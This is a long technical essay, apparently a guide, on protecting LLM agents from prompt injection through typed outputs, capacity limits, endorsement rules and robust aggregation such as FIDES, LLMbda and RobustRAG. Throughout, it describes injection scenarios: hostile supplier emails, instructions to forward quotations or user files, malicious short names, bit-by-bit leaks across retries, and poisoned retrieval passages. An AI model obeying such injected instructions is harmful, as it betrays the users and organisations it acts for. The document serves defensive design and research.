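Refusals are easier to overlook because the provider returns them outside the schema. When an OpenAI model declines a request for safety reasons, the response has a separate refusal field containing the model's explanation. OpenAI suggests showing this message to the user or handling it in code. In an agent, a developer might instead forward it to the main model to decide what to do next, although the program needs only the fact that the model refused. A supplier could provoke a refusal by asking for something dangerous in the email, and could try to control the wording of the explanation.

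An answer can also stop too early, either because it reaches the maximum number of tokens or because a content filter interrupts it. The mask ensures only that the partial output could have been continued into a valid answer. OpenAI's guide tells developers to check for both cases, even though it also advertises that they no longer need to validate the format. A program should not fill in the missing part with default values. If the output ended after the category and the program assumed that "urgent" was false, a supplier who could make answers run long could set that field to false.

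Error messages are the least obvious way for untrusted text to get out. A validator that rejects an order number may report "Unknown order: " followed by whatever the isolated model wrote. If the program sends this message to a privileged model for correction, the attacker's text reaches that model only because the value was rejected. Deleting the value from the message may not be enough, because an error about an unexpected field can quote the field's name, which the isolated model may also have made up.

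Standard libraries produce such messages. According to Anthropic's *Structured outputs*, when its Java library can't convert a response into the expected type, the error message includes the model's JSON response to help with diagnosis. Anthropic advises developers not to log these messages directly if they could contain sensitive information. In the mailbox, such logs carry the same risk as logged reasoning.

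The safe alternative is an error code from a fixed list. In the following sketch, every path out of the function returns either checked values or one of these codes:

```
def read_result(response, sender):
    if response is a refusal:          return error("REFUSED")
    if response is incomplete:         return error("INCOMPLETE")

    fields = parse_json(response.answer)
    if parsing failed:                 return error("BAD_FORM")
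    if fields do not fit SCHEMA:       return error("BAD_FIELD")

    if fields.category is "invoice":
        if due_date is not plausible:  return error("BAD_DATE")
        if order is not in ORDERS[sender]:

return error("BAD_ORDER")
        if amount does not match order:

return error("BAD_AMOUNT")

    return checked values only         # "reason" is dropped here
```

The attacker can still choose which error code comes back, so the error codes count as part of the output type. They can also reveal something about the data used in the checks, such as whether an order number exists. In the mailbox, the clerk looks at the email whichever error code comes back.

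### What providers recommend between agent steps

OpenAI's *Safety in building agents* advises developers to defend against prompt injection by designing workflows so that untrusted data never directly drives an agent's behaviour, and by extracting only specific structured fields, such as enums or validated JSON, from outside input. It argues that structured outputs between steps remove the free-form channels that attackers use to smuggle in instructions. It also warns against putting untrusted text into developer messages, which the model prioritises over user messages.

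This advice is close to the map-reduce design but less strict. OpenAI's examples of suitable constraints include fixed schemas and required field names, but a schema with fixed fields can still allow any string in each of them. The calendar example in OpenAI's guide to structured outputs has text fields for an event's name, date and participants. Anthropic's main example extracts a customer's details from an email into three text fields and one boolean. Both are reasonable ways to fill a database, but under Jacob and colleagues' rule only the boolean could go to a privileged model.

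The same OpenAI page later qualifies this, stating that structured outputs and isolation "greatly reduce, but don't fully remove" the risk when agents process arbitrary text that influences tool calls. The remaining risk comes partly from text fields, which a developer can eliminate, and partly from false values, which can satisfy even the strictest schema.

*Structured outputs*, from the smaller provider SubQ, gives advice that fits the mailbox more closely. The program should check for errors, refusals and truncation before parsing an answer, then validate the parsed JSON itself.

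### Whether the constraint makes answers worse

A format constraint can reduce accuracy by preventing the model from reasoning before it answers. OpenAI's Structured Outputs feature generates fields in the order the schema lists them. If "urgent" is the only field, the model's first meaningful token has to be true or false. This hardly matters for an obvious invoice, but it might for a long email that mentions a deadline only in the fourth paragraph.

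The remedy is to let the model reason before it gives the typed value. A reasoning model does this by default. With other models, the developer can put the "reason" field at the start of the schema and have the program delete it after parsing. If the field came last, the model could only use it to justify a choice it had already made. OpenAI's maths example lists the solution steps before the final answer. However, a 100-token explanation would increase the output from 20 to 120 tokens per email, or from 4,000 to 24,000 for the whole mailbox.

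In another version, one call answers freely and a second converts that answer into the schema. Both calls must be quarantined, because the free answer may contain instructions from the email. This version helps when a provider's constrained mode works badly with long reasoning, but it adds a call for every item.

Masking can also change the answer, because it is applied one token at a time. Suppose an email contains a haulage company's bill, and the model tends to call it a "delivery invoice", which is not one of the four categories. For the first token, the model gives "delivery" a probability of 0.6, "invoice" 0.3 and illegal tokens the remaining 0.1. Masking removes the illegal tokens, which raises the probability of "delivery" to 0.6/0.9, or 67%. After "delivery", the only legal continuation is "notice", even if the model gave it just a 5% chance. The program therefore files the bill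 as a delivery notice about two times out of three.

Comparing complete answers would have selected "invoice" 91% of the time, because the model's original probability was 0.3 for "invoice" and 0.6 × 0.05 = 0.03 for "delivery notice". Developers can reduce this effect by defining each label in the task prompt and choosing labels that don't start with the same word as anything a model might confuse them with. Short codes such as A, B, C and D avoid shared beginnings.

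Providers' advice points towards simple schemas. Databricks reports that heavily nested schemas reduce output quality and recommends flattening them. OpenAI recommends clear field names and descriptions, and testing to find the structure that works best for the task. These are rules of thumb, not findings from controlled experiments.

Research on typed defences gives only indirect evidence about whether constraining the output harms an agent's performance. Jacob and colleagues used providers' structured outputs in three agents. The shopping and calendar agents completed about as many tasks as the unprotected versions, which suggests that the constraint did little harm there. The software-repair agent did noticeably worse, which they attribute to the loss of the bug report's natural-language detail. Their experiment compared whole designs, so it can't separate the effect of the constraint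 from the effect of withholding text. Costa and colleagues left constrained decoding out of the version they tested because they found it unnecessary for most of the benchmark's tasks.

The company can measure the effect on its mailbox by having the clerk label a sample of past emails. It could then run the same model on them in three ways: with free text that code parses afterwards, with the constrained category alone, and with a reason field that comes before the category and is later deleted. If the category alone does worse than the other two, and those do equally well, the model needed room to reason and the mask itself didn't make the results worse.

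## How much influence a typed value can carry

An attacker who controls a map call can choose any value the schema allows. Capacity measures how much choice the attacker has. A result that can take N different values has a capacity of log₂ N bits. A boolean has two values, so its capacity is one bit, and each additional bit doubles the number of values.

| Type | Permitted values | Capacity |
|---|---|---|
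| Boolean | 2 | 1 bit |
| Enum with eight strings | 8 | 3 bits |
| Whole-number score from 0 to 10 | 11 | 3.5 bits |
| Date within one year | 365 | 8.5 bits |
| Name of 30 letters, digits or underscores | 63³⁰ | about 179 bits |
| Integer with no range | unlimited | unlimited |

The figure for the name depends on the alphabet. With lower-case letters alone, it would be 141 bits.

These figures are upper limits, since an attacker may not fully control what the model answers. They are the right figures to use because the threat model assumes full control. Capacity doesn't measure harm, since one bit that decides whether the company pays an invoice can matter more than the eight and a half bits in a date.

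### Adding up the mailbox

The capacities of separate results add up because their numbers of possible values multiply. The "urgent" field alone produces 200 booleans for the 200 emails, with a total capacity of 200 bits. A supplier who wrote three of the emails controls only three of those booleans, or 3 bits, and so can choose among eight combinations.

The category adds 2 bits per email, which brings the full schema to 3 bits per email. That is 600 bits for the mailbox and 9 bits for the supplier with three emails. An answer can also fail the checks, in which case the email goes to the clerk. Counting that as a ninth outcome raises the capacity to 3.2 bits per email.

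If all 200 emails shared one call, a single malicious email could choose all 600 bits.

### The type lattice in FIDES

The mailbox code only moves emails between folders, so it can act on an untrusted category without much risk. An agent that sends messages or makes payments needs a rule for when an untrusted value may affect those actions. Such a rule, called endorsement, lets the program treat a value derived from untrusted data as trusted.

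Costa and colleagues build endorsement into the trust labels of FIDES. When the system combines two pieces of data, the result takes the less trusted label, an operation called a join. So once the planner reads one untrusted email, everything it writes is untrusted, and the usual policy blocks it from taking consequential actions.

FIDES can add a type to each label. The types form a lattice, an order in which any two elements have a join, and capacity determines their position:

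```
bool  ⊑  enum["a", "b", "c"]  ⊑  string
```

A boolean or an enum can carry a limited amount of information, while a string can carry any amount. If a quarantined model answers a yes-or-no question about an untrusted email, the answer has the label (untrusted, bool). A free-text summary of the same email has the label (untrusted, string). A policy can accept the boolean for a consequential action and refuse the string, because the boolean gives the email's author at most one bit of influence over the action.

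In one example, a user wants three emails checked for a meeting request, and the planner receives a boolean that indicates whether they contain one. If it is true, the planner has the quarantined model extract the event details into a variable the planner can't read, then passes that variable to the calendar tool. A strict policy would block the calendar call because the planner has received a value derived from the emails, but the looser policy permits it.

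The one-bit limit applies only to the decision to create an event. The email's author can also choose the date, the time and the participants, which reach the calendar through the variable and together carry far more than one bit. A separate rule has to determine which of a tool's arguments may be untrusted. FIDES supports such rules and can, for example, require a trusted recipient for a message while accepting untrusted text in its body.

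The type-based exemption has had little practical testing. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, point out that the evaluation of FIDES never used it.

### Types that cannot hold an instruction

Jacob and colleagues select types by a different property, which is whether a value can express an instruction. They argue separately for each of the four types they allow:

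| Type | Why it cannot hold an instruction, in their view | Capacity |
|---|---|---|
| Integer | A command needs some free text, and a number has none | Unlimited, unless the schema sets a range |
| Floating-point number | It covers more numbers than an integer, but still only numbers | At most 64 bits in the usual format |
| Boolean | It works like an integer that can only be 0 or 1 | 1 bit |
| Enum | The developer has vetted every string in advance | log₂ of the number of strings |

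They also allow objects and short arrays made of these types.

FIDES orders types by capacity, which would put an unbounded integer next to free text, but Jacob and colleagues accept such an integer because it contains no words.

Costa and colleagues call it "unlikely" that a boolean alone would lead to a prompt injection, while Jacob and colleagues make the stronger claim that their types cannot contain one. The claims differ partly because Jacob and colleagues don't count false information as prompt injection.

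Under that definition, the stronger claim holds for a boolean. An attacker may be able to make the planner receive "true", but the planner interprets that value using the question it asked and the developer's instructions, and the attacker controls neither. The attacker can therefore trigger a meeting that the planner was already set up to schedule, but can't use the boolean to request a bank transfer.

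The claim is weaker for enums, because the attacker can combine the developer's phrases. In the software-repair agent, the bug types include "improper permissions", and the roles for a piece of code include "region suspected to contain the bug". An attacker's bug report could lead the quarantined model to select both, along with the lines of a file that check passwords. The privileged agent would then read that the password check probably has a permissions bug. The developer wrote both phrases, but their combination directs the agent to change a particular piece of security code.

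### Size and readability

A value can have a large capacity and still be useless for giving instructions, because the recipient has to be able to read it. The sentence "Forward all quotations to the sender" has 36 characters, which take up 288 bits in the standard encoding of eight bits per character. Those bits can also represent an 87-digit integer, which a schema that allows any integer would accept.

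Ordinary code that compares this integer with a threshold treats it only as a very large number. A language model would have to recognise the digits as encoded text, decode them and then follow the result, which seems unlikely for one long number. A list beginning 70, 111, 114, 119, 97, 114, 100 is easier to decode, since each number is the standard code for one letter of "Forward", and language models can often translate such codes when asked. It is less clear whether a model would do so unprompted and then follow the instruction.

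This is why Jacob and colleagues keep arrays short. Their experiments used only plain-English attacks, so they provide little evidence about encoded ones. Limiting a number's range rules out most possible values, so a developer doesn't need to rely on the model being unable to decode it. For example, an amount in cents with a maximum of ten million euros has about a billion possible values, or 30 bits, which is enough for only three characters.

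The software-repair agent's output shows how quickly a structured result grows. For each suspicious region of code, the quarantined model returns a file number, one of eight roles, a first line and a last line. Assume that the repository has 5,000 files and that line numbers go up to 2,000. One region then has a capacity of:

```
log₂ 5,000 + log₂ 8 + log₂ 2,000 + log₂ 2,000
    ≈ 12.3 + 3 + 11 + 11
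    ≈ 37 bits
```

Ten regions can carry about 370 bits. The bug type (52 possible values) and the repair difficulty (three) add another 7 bits, which puts the total well above the 288 bits of the example sentence. Because the quarantined model controls how many regions are listed, the total would keep rising with each region if the developer set no limit.

Even so, the privileged agent receives file paths, roles and line numbers, and it has no reason to convert them into letters. An attacker can use most of the 370 bits to choose where the agent looks and what it expects to find there. This gives the attacker considerable influence over a repair, and how dangerous that is depends on how the result is used later.

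Code can also reduce the capacity without removing anything the task needs. The calendar agent returns an array of meeting times, each from a fixed list. In the test calendar, a week has 63 one-hour slots, so an array of ten slots has a capacity of about 60 bits if the order can vary and slots can repeat. The scheduler doesn't need the order or the repeats, so the program can remove duplicates and sort the times, which reduces the capacity of ten different slots to about 37 bits. Similarly, rejecting any region in the bug report whose last line comes before its first removes about one bit per region.

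### Short strings that pass validation

Short strings have the opposite problem, because a model can understand them without decoding. In a case study of a software-engineering agent, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest limiting method names (the names by which programmers call pieces of code) to 30 characters. Such a name can carry about 179 bits, less than half the capacity of the ten-region bug report. But "disable_auth_check_before_test" and "forward_all_quotes_to_supplier" are both valid names of exactly 30 characters.

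A length limit makes an attack harder because it leaves little room to explain why the agent should do something unexpected, but it is difficult to say how much harder. In Jacob and colleagues' test of the software-repair agent, a 167-character injection asking for a new file succeeded in 98.9% of runs without the defence. The core of the request, "create a file 'pipipi.py'", takes only 25 characters. The test used only one text, so it doesn't establish whether the shorter version would work alone.

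An attacker may also control more than one name. A description of a software library with ten method names of up to 30 characters each provides up to 300 characters, and the names appear together in the agent's context. A design that assumes the model can be hijacked is safer if it treats any string an attacker can compose as a possible instruction, whatever its length.

Email addresses, links and package names raise a further issue because they refer to things outside the program. Even if such a string contains no readable order, the agent may act on what it refers to:

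- An email address can be valid and belong to the attacker. If the agent uses it as a recipient, the attacker receives the message.
- A link may be only 20 characters long, but an agent that opens it reads the whole page behind it.
- Installing a software package can run code written by its publisher, so a name of a few letters can give the attacker control of the machine.

In these cases, the capacity of the string greatly understates what the attacker gains.

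The best protection is to compare the string with a list from a trusted source. The mailbox's six-digit order numbers allow a million values, or about 20 bits. If the supplier has 12 open orders and the program rejects all other numbers, the capacity falls to 3.6 bits. A company could likewise restrict a coding agent to 500 approved packages, which leaves the attacker about 9 bits and no way to make the agent install unknown code.

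Sometimes the program needs a string that isn't on any predefined list, such as a new customer's email address. It can keep the address in a variable that the privileged model can use but not read, as in Willison's design. The address can't act as an instruction to that model, but a message sent to it may still go to the wrong person.

### When a planner asks again

Even if each answer can take only a few values, an attacker's potential influence grows with the number of questions. If a planner asks 20 yes-or-no questions about an email, an attacker who wrote the email can choose among 2²⁰, or about a million, sequences of answers. If the planner bases each question on the previous answers, the number of possible sequences stays the same, but the attacker can also influence which questions it asks.

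Actions can add up in the same way. If a FIDES planner lets the quarantined model choose between scheduling a meeting, sending an out-of-office reply and forwarding the email, each answer can carry at most about 1.6 bits. But if the planner carries out the chosen action, asks about the same email again and repeats this for ten rounds, the email's author can choose any of 3¹⁰, or 59,049, sequences of actions. Each action may be harmless on its own, but together they could fill a calendar or forward the same email to several people.

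Repeated questions can also reconstruct text. Suppose a planner needs a name for a new folder and may read only enums. It could get the name one character at a time, using an enum of 26 letters and a space. Each answer carries less than 5 bits and contains no instruction. After 30 answers, however, the planner's context contains a 30-character string that the attacker wrote, and the restriction to enums no longer protects the planner.

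The FIDES lattice doesn't track this accumulation. Joining bool with bool gives bool, so a planner that has read 20 untrusted booleans has the same type in its label as one that has read only one. A policy that accepts this label because one bit is too little influence to matter would also accept 20 bits. To limit the total, the system would need to count the bits from each author.

The same arithmetic applies to secrets leaving the system. Garby and colleagues describe a weakness in CaMeL, another defence based on two models. CaMeL tracks labels during each attempt at a task but not in the loop that retries failed attempts, so an attack that leaks one bit per attempt can reveal a whole secret over many attempts.

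The mailbox program avoids the problem because it uses the same question once for each email. Before the first call, its developer can calculate each supplier's total influence from the number of emails. The developer can't do this if a planner generates its own follow-up questions.

### Restricting endorsement

Garby and colleagues treat endorsement as an explicit operation in LLMbda, a small programming language for agents. Every value has a label, and the function `endorse` changes an untrusted value's label to trusted. In their main example, a quarantined model classifies an email, and the agent uses the category as the subject line of an automatic reply. The function that sends the reply rejects untrusted subject lines, so the program has to endorse the category first.

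Unrestricted use of `endorse` would let an agent trust anything. The language's one built-in restriction is that `endorse` has no effect in a branch the program entered because of an untrusted value. Everything the program computes there is untrusted, so code that a model builds from a malicious email can't endorse its own data.

That restriction fails if the program endorsed the malicious text at an earlier stage. Code built from the text then counts as trusted, and the endorsements inside it take effect. An appendix proposes a stricter function, robust_endorse, to prevent this. It permanently marks every value it endorses, and any value computed from a marked value inherits the mark. The program stops if it tries to endorse a marked value. The developer also has to prevent generated code from calling the unrestricted endorse function directly.

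Developers can also use the mark to restrict where a value is used. Each policy must specify whether marked values are allowed, so a developer could allow an endorsed category in a subject line but require an unmarked value for the recipient of a payment.

A second function, bounded_endorse, limits the amount of information that a single endorsement can carry. It endorses a value only if the value is in a fixed list. In the mailbox, it would work roughly as follows:

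```
def bounded_endorse(value):
    ALLOWED = ["invoice", "delivery notice",
               "price change", "other"]

    copy = endorse(value)       # a copy labelled as trusted
    if copy in ALLOWED:
        return copy
    else:
        return value            # the original, still untrusted
```

If the list has n strings, one endorsement can carry at most log₂ n bits of the attacker's choice, which is 2 bits here. The developer has to fix the list in advance, for the same reason as with an enum. If a value is outside the list, the program continues, but the value stays untrusted and any function that requires trusted data will reject it.

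The function must endorse the value before checking it because of the built-in restriction. If it checked the untrusted original, the result of the check would also be untrusted, and an endorsement in the branch that followed would have no effect. The function therefore checks a trusted copy and releases it only if it matches the list.

Garby and colleagues don't formally prove what either function achieves, and they leave a proof of the limit in bits to future work. The limit applies to each endorsement separately, so a program that calls bounded_endorse on 100 different answers from the same author can pass on 200 bits. Adding the permanent mark wouldn't prevent this, because each new answer starts unmarked.

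Some tasks need values that no short list can contain. Garby and colleagues tested a banking agent that reads a bill from a file and pays it, so it has to endorse an account number and an amount. bounded_endorse would reject both. robust_endorse would accept them, but it doesn't restrict which account number the file's author supplies, so a fraudulent one could get through. Garby and colleagues justify the endorsement on the grounds that a user who asks an agent to pay the bill in a file has chosen to trust that file. The agent writes the endorsement into its plan before it reads the file, so the file can't add further endorsements.

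A person can also make the decision while the agent is running. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) extends FIDES with an agent that can ask its user to endorse untrusted data. In the paper's example, an email lists ten tasks, each requiring an action that the policy would normally block. The user can endorse the email once instead of approving ten actions. This endorsement covers the whole text, so it doesn't limit how many bits the email can pass to the agent, and its safety depends on whether the user notices anything wrong with the email.

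## Combining the results

When the map calls have finished, the mailbox program holds up to 200 checked results, and a hostile supplier may have chosen the values in some of them. The reduce step combines the results into something the company can use, such as sorted folders, a total or an email to a colleague. How much a false value can affect that output depends on the operation used to combine them.

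### Code or a second model

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe two versions of the reduce step, which need different safeguards. If ordinary code performs the step, it can't follow an instruction hidden in a value, but the developer has to express the task as a fixed operation and choose one whose result a few false values can't change much. Moving each email to the folder for its category meets both conditions.

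A model with tools can handle less predictable tasks, such as writing an email about the results, but the program then has to restrict everything the model reads. Each map result needs a type that can't hold an instruction, and so does anything that accompanies it, such as a file name or subject line. In Jacob and colleagues' shopping agent, a quarantined model turns each customer review into two integers, which rate how strongly the review supports the product and how relevant it is. The model that decides what to buy receives the integers but not the review.

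A model that reads only typed outputs is protected from injected commands, but nobody can calculate in advance how far one false integer will shift its decision. It may also miscount a long list. A developer can avoid both problems by having code do the arithmetic and giving the model only the result to put into a sentence. For example, 200 "urgent" booleans, one per email, carry 200 bits, while a count of the urgent emails has 201 possible values and carries 7.7 bits.

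### What one hostile item can change

The table shows how much an attacker who controls one of n items can change the result, compared with what it would have been had the answer for that item been honest.

| Operation | Effect of one hostile item |
|---|---|
| Filter | Includes or excludes that item only |
| Any (true if at least one item is true) | Can make the result true, but can't make it false if another item is true |
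| All (true only if every item is true) | Can make the result false, but can't make it true if another item is false |
| Count | Changes by at most 1 |
| Sum | Changes by at most the width of the permitted range |
| Mean | Changes by at most the width of the range divided by n |
| Median | Moves by at most one position in the sorted list |
| Top K | Gains or loses one place, which lets another item in or pushes one out |
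| Majority vote | Changes the winner's lead by at most two votes |

Of these, only the filter limits the effect of a false value to the item it came from. The mailbox program sorts email this way, so a supplier who falsifies an email's category misfiles only that email.

The "any" rule suits warnings because a false alarm causes the clerk little trouble. A supplier can keep its own email from triggering a warning, but it can't suppress one triggered by somebody else's email. The "all" rule suits approvals because a hostile document can't force a payment through if a legitimate document's result is "no", although it can block the payment.

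The range the schema allows for a value determines how much one email can change a sum or mean. If an amount has no upper limit, one email can make the total as large as its author likes. A count is safer, but a small change can still matter if an action depends on a threshold. If the company plans to raise its own prices once 20 suppliers have announced increases, and 19 have, one false "price change" is enough to trigger the rise.

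### Several hostile items and the breakdown point

Suppose the map calls score emails from 0 to 10 for the seriousness of a delivery delay. Nine honest emails receive the scores 2, 3, 3, 4, 4, 4, 5, 5 and 6, which have a mean and a median of 4. An attacker then adds emails that all score 10:

| Fake tens added | Share of all scores | Mean | Median |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | 0% | 4.0 | 4 |
| 1 | 10% | 4.6 | 4 |
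| 3 | 25% | 5.5 | 4.5 |
| 8 | 47% | 6.8 | 6 |
| 9 | 50% | 7.0 | 8 |
| 10 | 53% | 7.2 | 10 |

Every fake score shifts the mean. The median shifts more slowly and stays within the range of the honest scores as long as the fake scores are a minority. Once they are the majority, the attacker sets the median directly, and it ends up further from the honest result than the mean does.

Statisticians describe this limit with the breakdown point, the smallest share of the inputs that an attacker must control to push the result as far as they like. The median has a breakdown point of one half. If the inputs can be any number, a single one is enough to move the mean this way, however many honest ones there are. Restricting the inputs to a fixed range limits how far the mean can move. On the 0-to-10 scale, fake scores of 10 raise the mean by their share of the inputs times the distance from the honest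 mean to 10. If the honest mean is 4, three fakes among 12 scores raise it by 0.25 × 6 = 1.5.

Despite its high breakdown point, the median can have a large error even below that point, because fake values can still move it anywhere among the honest ones. If five reviewers give a product 0 and four give it 10, the median is 0. Adding two fake scores of 10 raises the median to 10, while the mean rises only from 4.4 to 5.5. The median therefore protects best when honest scores are close together, and developers should check that they are on real data before relying on it.

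### When one author sends many items

A supplier who wants more than half the scores only has to send more emails, since each one gets its own answer.

The most direct remedy is to limit each sender's influence. The program can first take the median of each sender's scores, then the median of those medians. If the nine honest emails came from nine suppliers and a tenth supplier sent all ten fakes, the fakes count as a single score of 10 and the overall median stays at 4. To succeed, the attacker now has to control many senders.

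The limit depends on how the program identifies a sender. An email's author can type any name as the sender, and anyone can open 20 free email accounts. A safer method is to check that the domain authenticated by the mail server is on the company's list of suppliers, and to treat several domains owned by one supplier as a single sender.

The program can also give known suppliers more weight than strangers. In a weighted median, half the total weight lies on each side of the result, so an attacker needs half the weight, rather than half the emails, to control the result. If a stranger's email counts for a tenth of a supplier's, ten fake emails from new accounts count as much as one from a supplier. However, an attacker who breaks into a real supplier's account gets that supplier's full weight.

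Removing duplicates stops the simplest attacks, in which someone sends the same text many times. Code can find exact copies, but an attacker can have a model write 50 different versions of a message. Looser matching would catch more of these but also discard honest emails about the same late lorry.

Duplicate removal can also break isolation. If the program keeps the newest copy of similar texts, a hostile supplier could copy a competitor's email, add a hidden paragraph and have the program discard the original. Keeping the oldest copy prevents this attack. Comparing only emails from the same sender is safer still, because no supplier can then remove another's email.

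### The product recommender

Product reviews raise all of these problems. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe a recommender that compares products in a category, such as toasters, using reviews from an online shop. An attacker may write a review to promote one product or discredit its rivals.

The design therefore requires that a review affect only the product it belongs to, and that no single review have an unduly large effect on that product. Each map call rates one review on fixed categories such as "good price" and "easy to use", and the reduce step combines the ratings and recommends the top K products. The user may not know which categories matter for an unfamiliar product, so a model can suggest some, but only before it sees any reviews.

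As with the emails, the program itself must record which product each review belongs to and not leave this to the map call.

Even then, the first requirement holds for ratings but not for rankings. A false review can't change a rival's rating, but if it lifts the product it reviews into the top K, another product drops out. Similarly, if code rescales the ratings so that the best product gets a 10, an inflated top rating lowers every other score.

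Whether the program meets the second requirement depends on the number of reviews. On a 0-to-10 scale, one false answer can move the mean of 300 reviews by at most 0.03, but it can move the mean of three reviews by up to 3.3. A list of the highest averages therefore favours attackers who promote new products with few reviews. Requiring a minimum number of reviews helps, as does starting each product's score at the category average and letting its reviews move the score gradually. Neither measure stops a seller who can buy hundreds of reviews from different accounts.

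Beurer-Kellner and colleagues point out that a malicious review that scores well in every category achieves no more than an ordinary glowing review. The program is therefore as vulnerable to fake reviews as the shop's own star ratings are.

### Voting across documents in RobustRAG

Sometimes several documents answer the same question, and the program can compare their answers. This is common in retrieval-augmented generation (RAG), in which a program searches a collection for passages relevant to a question and gives them to a model with the question. An ordinary RAG program puts all the passages in one prompt, so one bad passage can decide the answer. In *Logic Hijacking of RAG* (2026), a small Llama model read the five highest-ranked passages for each question. A single planted passage, averaging 40 words, made the model give the attacker's answer to 82 of 100 questions on each of two datasets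 and 40 of 100 on a third.

Xiang, Wu and colleagues (2024) proposed RobustRAG in *Certifiably Robust RAG against Retrieval Corruption*. This defence has the model answer the question from each passage separately, then combines the answers. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues cite it as similar to their code-based reduce step. Neighbouring passages can also share a model call. Larger groups give better answers when there is no attack, but one malicious passage then corrupts its whole group.

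For multiple-choice questions, RobustRAG takes a majority vote. If the top answer's lead among the honest passages is larger than the number of malicious passages, the attacker can't change the outcome. With six honest votes for one answer and two for another, the lead is four, so three malicious passages can't change the outcome, but four can force a tie.

Free text is harder to count, because "Mount Everest" and "Everest is the highest" are the same answer in different words. Xiang and colleagues use two methods:

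- Keyword aggregation extracts the important words and phrases from each answer and counts how many answers contain them. A final model call receives the question and the common keywords, but none of the passages.
- Decoding aggregation works while the model writes. At each step, the program adds up the probabilities that the isolated calls give to each possible next token. Each call can add at most 1 to a token's total, so one malicious passage can't overcome a lead of more than 1. When the lead is too small, the program can use the token the model would have chosen without any passages.

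Keyword aggregation passes free text to the final model only if enough answers share it. With the settings for short answers, a keyword must appear in at least a fifth of the answers or in three, whichever is fewer. If all ten passages give an answer, the threshold is two, so one malicious passage can't introduce a word on its own. If only five passages give an answer, the threshold falls to one, and the malicious passage's words get through.

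The certificate in the title is a worst-case score for a test question. A procedure computes every response the system could give if an attacker inserted a set number of passages with any content, then records the lowest score. Unlike a measured attack success rate, this score also covers attacks not yet invented. The procedure needs the uncorrupted passages and the correct answer, so it can evaluate the method on test questions but can't guarantee the answer to a new question.

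The main tests used Mistral-7B and Llama-2-7B, which are now several generations old, with one malicious passage out of ten. Xiang and colleagues could certify 69 to 71% of multiple-choice answers and 26 to 38% of short answers. Actual prompt injections succeeded on 66 to 100% of questions without the defence and on at most 15% with it. Certified accuracy fell as the number of malicious passages grew and reached zero at five out of ten, when benign passages no longer outnumbered malicious ones. RobustRAG took 1.2 to 3.7 times as long as ordinary RAG.

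The votes have to come from different documents. Asking a model the same question several times and taking the most frequent answer is a common way to improve its accuracy, but *SecInfer* (2025) found that this gives little protection against prompt injection, because the injected text is in the prompt every time and can change most of the answers.

Voting also needs several documents that address the same question. For example, it could help if the company wanted to know whether fuel surcharges had risen that month and 30 hauliers had written about them. It can't help the company file an individual email, because the other 199 emails contain no information about whether that one is an invoice.

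### Newer methods and the honest majority

Later researchers criticised RobustRAG for losing too much information. *ReliabilityRAG* (Shen, Imana and colleagues, 2025) keeps RobustRAG's isolated answers but uses them to choose which documents to trust. A second, smaller model checks each pair of answers for contradictions. The program then finds the largest group of documents whose answers don't contradict one another, preferring the group with higher-ranked documents if there is a tie. It gives those documents in full to the main model.

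With GPT-4o-mini and ten documents, this method scored 80 out of 100 for writing short biographies, and about 78 when the top-ranked document contained an injection. RobustRAG scored about 61 without the injection and about 60 with it. The formal guarantee covers attackers who control up to a fifth of the documents, provided the contradiction checker rarely makes mistakes. With a perfect checker, it covers attackers who control any share below half.

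Xiang and colleagues ignore search rankings because an attacker can manipulate them, but Shen and colleagues argue that rankings are hard to fake, since search engines have spent more than two decades fighting manipulation. A ranking's value as evidence depends on how hard it is to fake, and faking one is hard for a popular web search but easy for an obscure one. A mailbox has no such ranking, and the list of known suppliers is the closest equivalent.

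Two methods from 2026 look for agreement in embeddings or other internal representations, which are lists of numbers that a model computes from a text. Tan, Zheng and colleagues (2026), in *PRA-RAG*, object to the number of model calls RobustRAG needs. Their method compares small combinations of passages and selects one close to most of the others. On one dataset with a fifth of the passages poisoned, accuracy was 71% and the attack success rate was 1%. The method's guarantee requires most of the combinations to contain no poisoned passages, which is stricter than requiring most of the passages to be clean. Ten passages form 45 pairs, of which 28 are clean if two passages are poisoned but only 21 if three are, so with pairs the guarantee covers at most two poisoned passages in ten. Tan and colleagues designed the method mainly to defend against false facts, not prompt injection.

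In *RAGSentinel*, Quan, Gao and colleagues (2026) measure how each passage changes a separate model's internal state. They compare these changes with their geometric median, the point with the smallest total distance to all of them, and discard the passages whose changes are outliers. They warn that attackers can defeat defences that only check whether texts are consistent by writing several poisoned documents that agree with one another. Their guarantee requires that fewer than half the passages be poisoned and that poisoned passages change the model's internal state in a measurably different way from honest ones, but they don't claim that every false passage will do so.

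These guarantees all depend on some kind of honest majority. That assumption is reasonable for the top results of a web search, but not where anyone can easily add documents. *Rescuing the Unpoisoned* (2025) tested a filter called RAGDefender with ten poisoned passages for every honest one. The attack success rate was 18%, compared with 99% without a defence. This is a good result in a setting where voting would fail, but the measured rate is not guaranteed.

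### Selected documents that return to a model

ReliabilityRAG and RAGSentinel both end by putting the documents that pass their filters into one prompt. This is acceptable if the worst outcome is a wrong answer and the filter removes documents that support one. It is more dangerous in an agent with tools. A document could contain both the correct answer and an instruction to forward the user's files. A filter based on contradictions would keep the document because its answer matches the others, and the instruction would reach the final model.

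Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe this problem in their résumé screener. One version ranks résumés by their similarity to the job requirements and then has a model summarise the top K. The ranking is safe from injection because no model reads the résumés at that stage. The summary isn't, because the model reads the K résumés together and any one of them can change what it writes about the rest. An applicant can get into the top K by matching the wording of the public job advertisement. Scoring each résumé in an isolated call first doesn't help if the summary still uses the full text.

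Selection can even concentrate the attacks. If three of the 200 emails are hostile, they make up 1.5% of the mailbox. But if each one makes its map call return the maximum score, and the program passes the ten highest-scoring emails to a second model, they could make up 30% of what that model reads.

For the résumés, a privileged model that has seen only the user's request and the job advertisement writes a template, which is a sentence with blanks, such as one stating how many more years of experience the best candidate has than the others. Isolated calls extract the years from each résumé, and code does the subtraction and fills in the blanks. An applicant can still lie about their own experience, or make the isolated call misreport it, but can't change what the summary says about another candidate's record.

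Whether the invoice example is secure depends on the same choice, because Beurer-Kellner and colleagues don't specify whether the model that writes the email to accounting reads the files.

| How the program prepares the email | What one malicious file can do |
|---|---|
| The model reads all the selected files, writes the email and sends it | Change the amounts reported for other invoices, or have the other files sent to an outside address |
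| The model knows only how many files there are and writes a covering note; code attaches the files unread and sends them to a fixed address | Get itself attached or left out |
| Code fills a table with a checked amount and order number for each file | Get itself listed or left out, or supply a false amount or order number that passes the checks |

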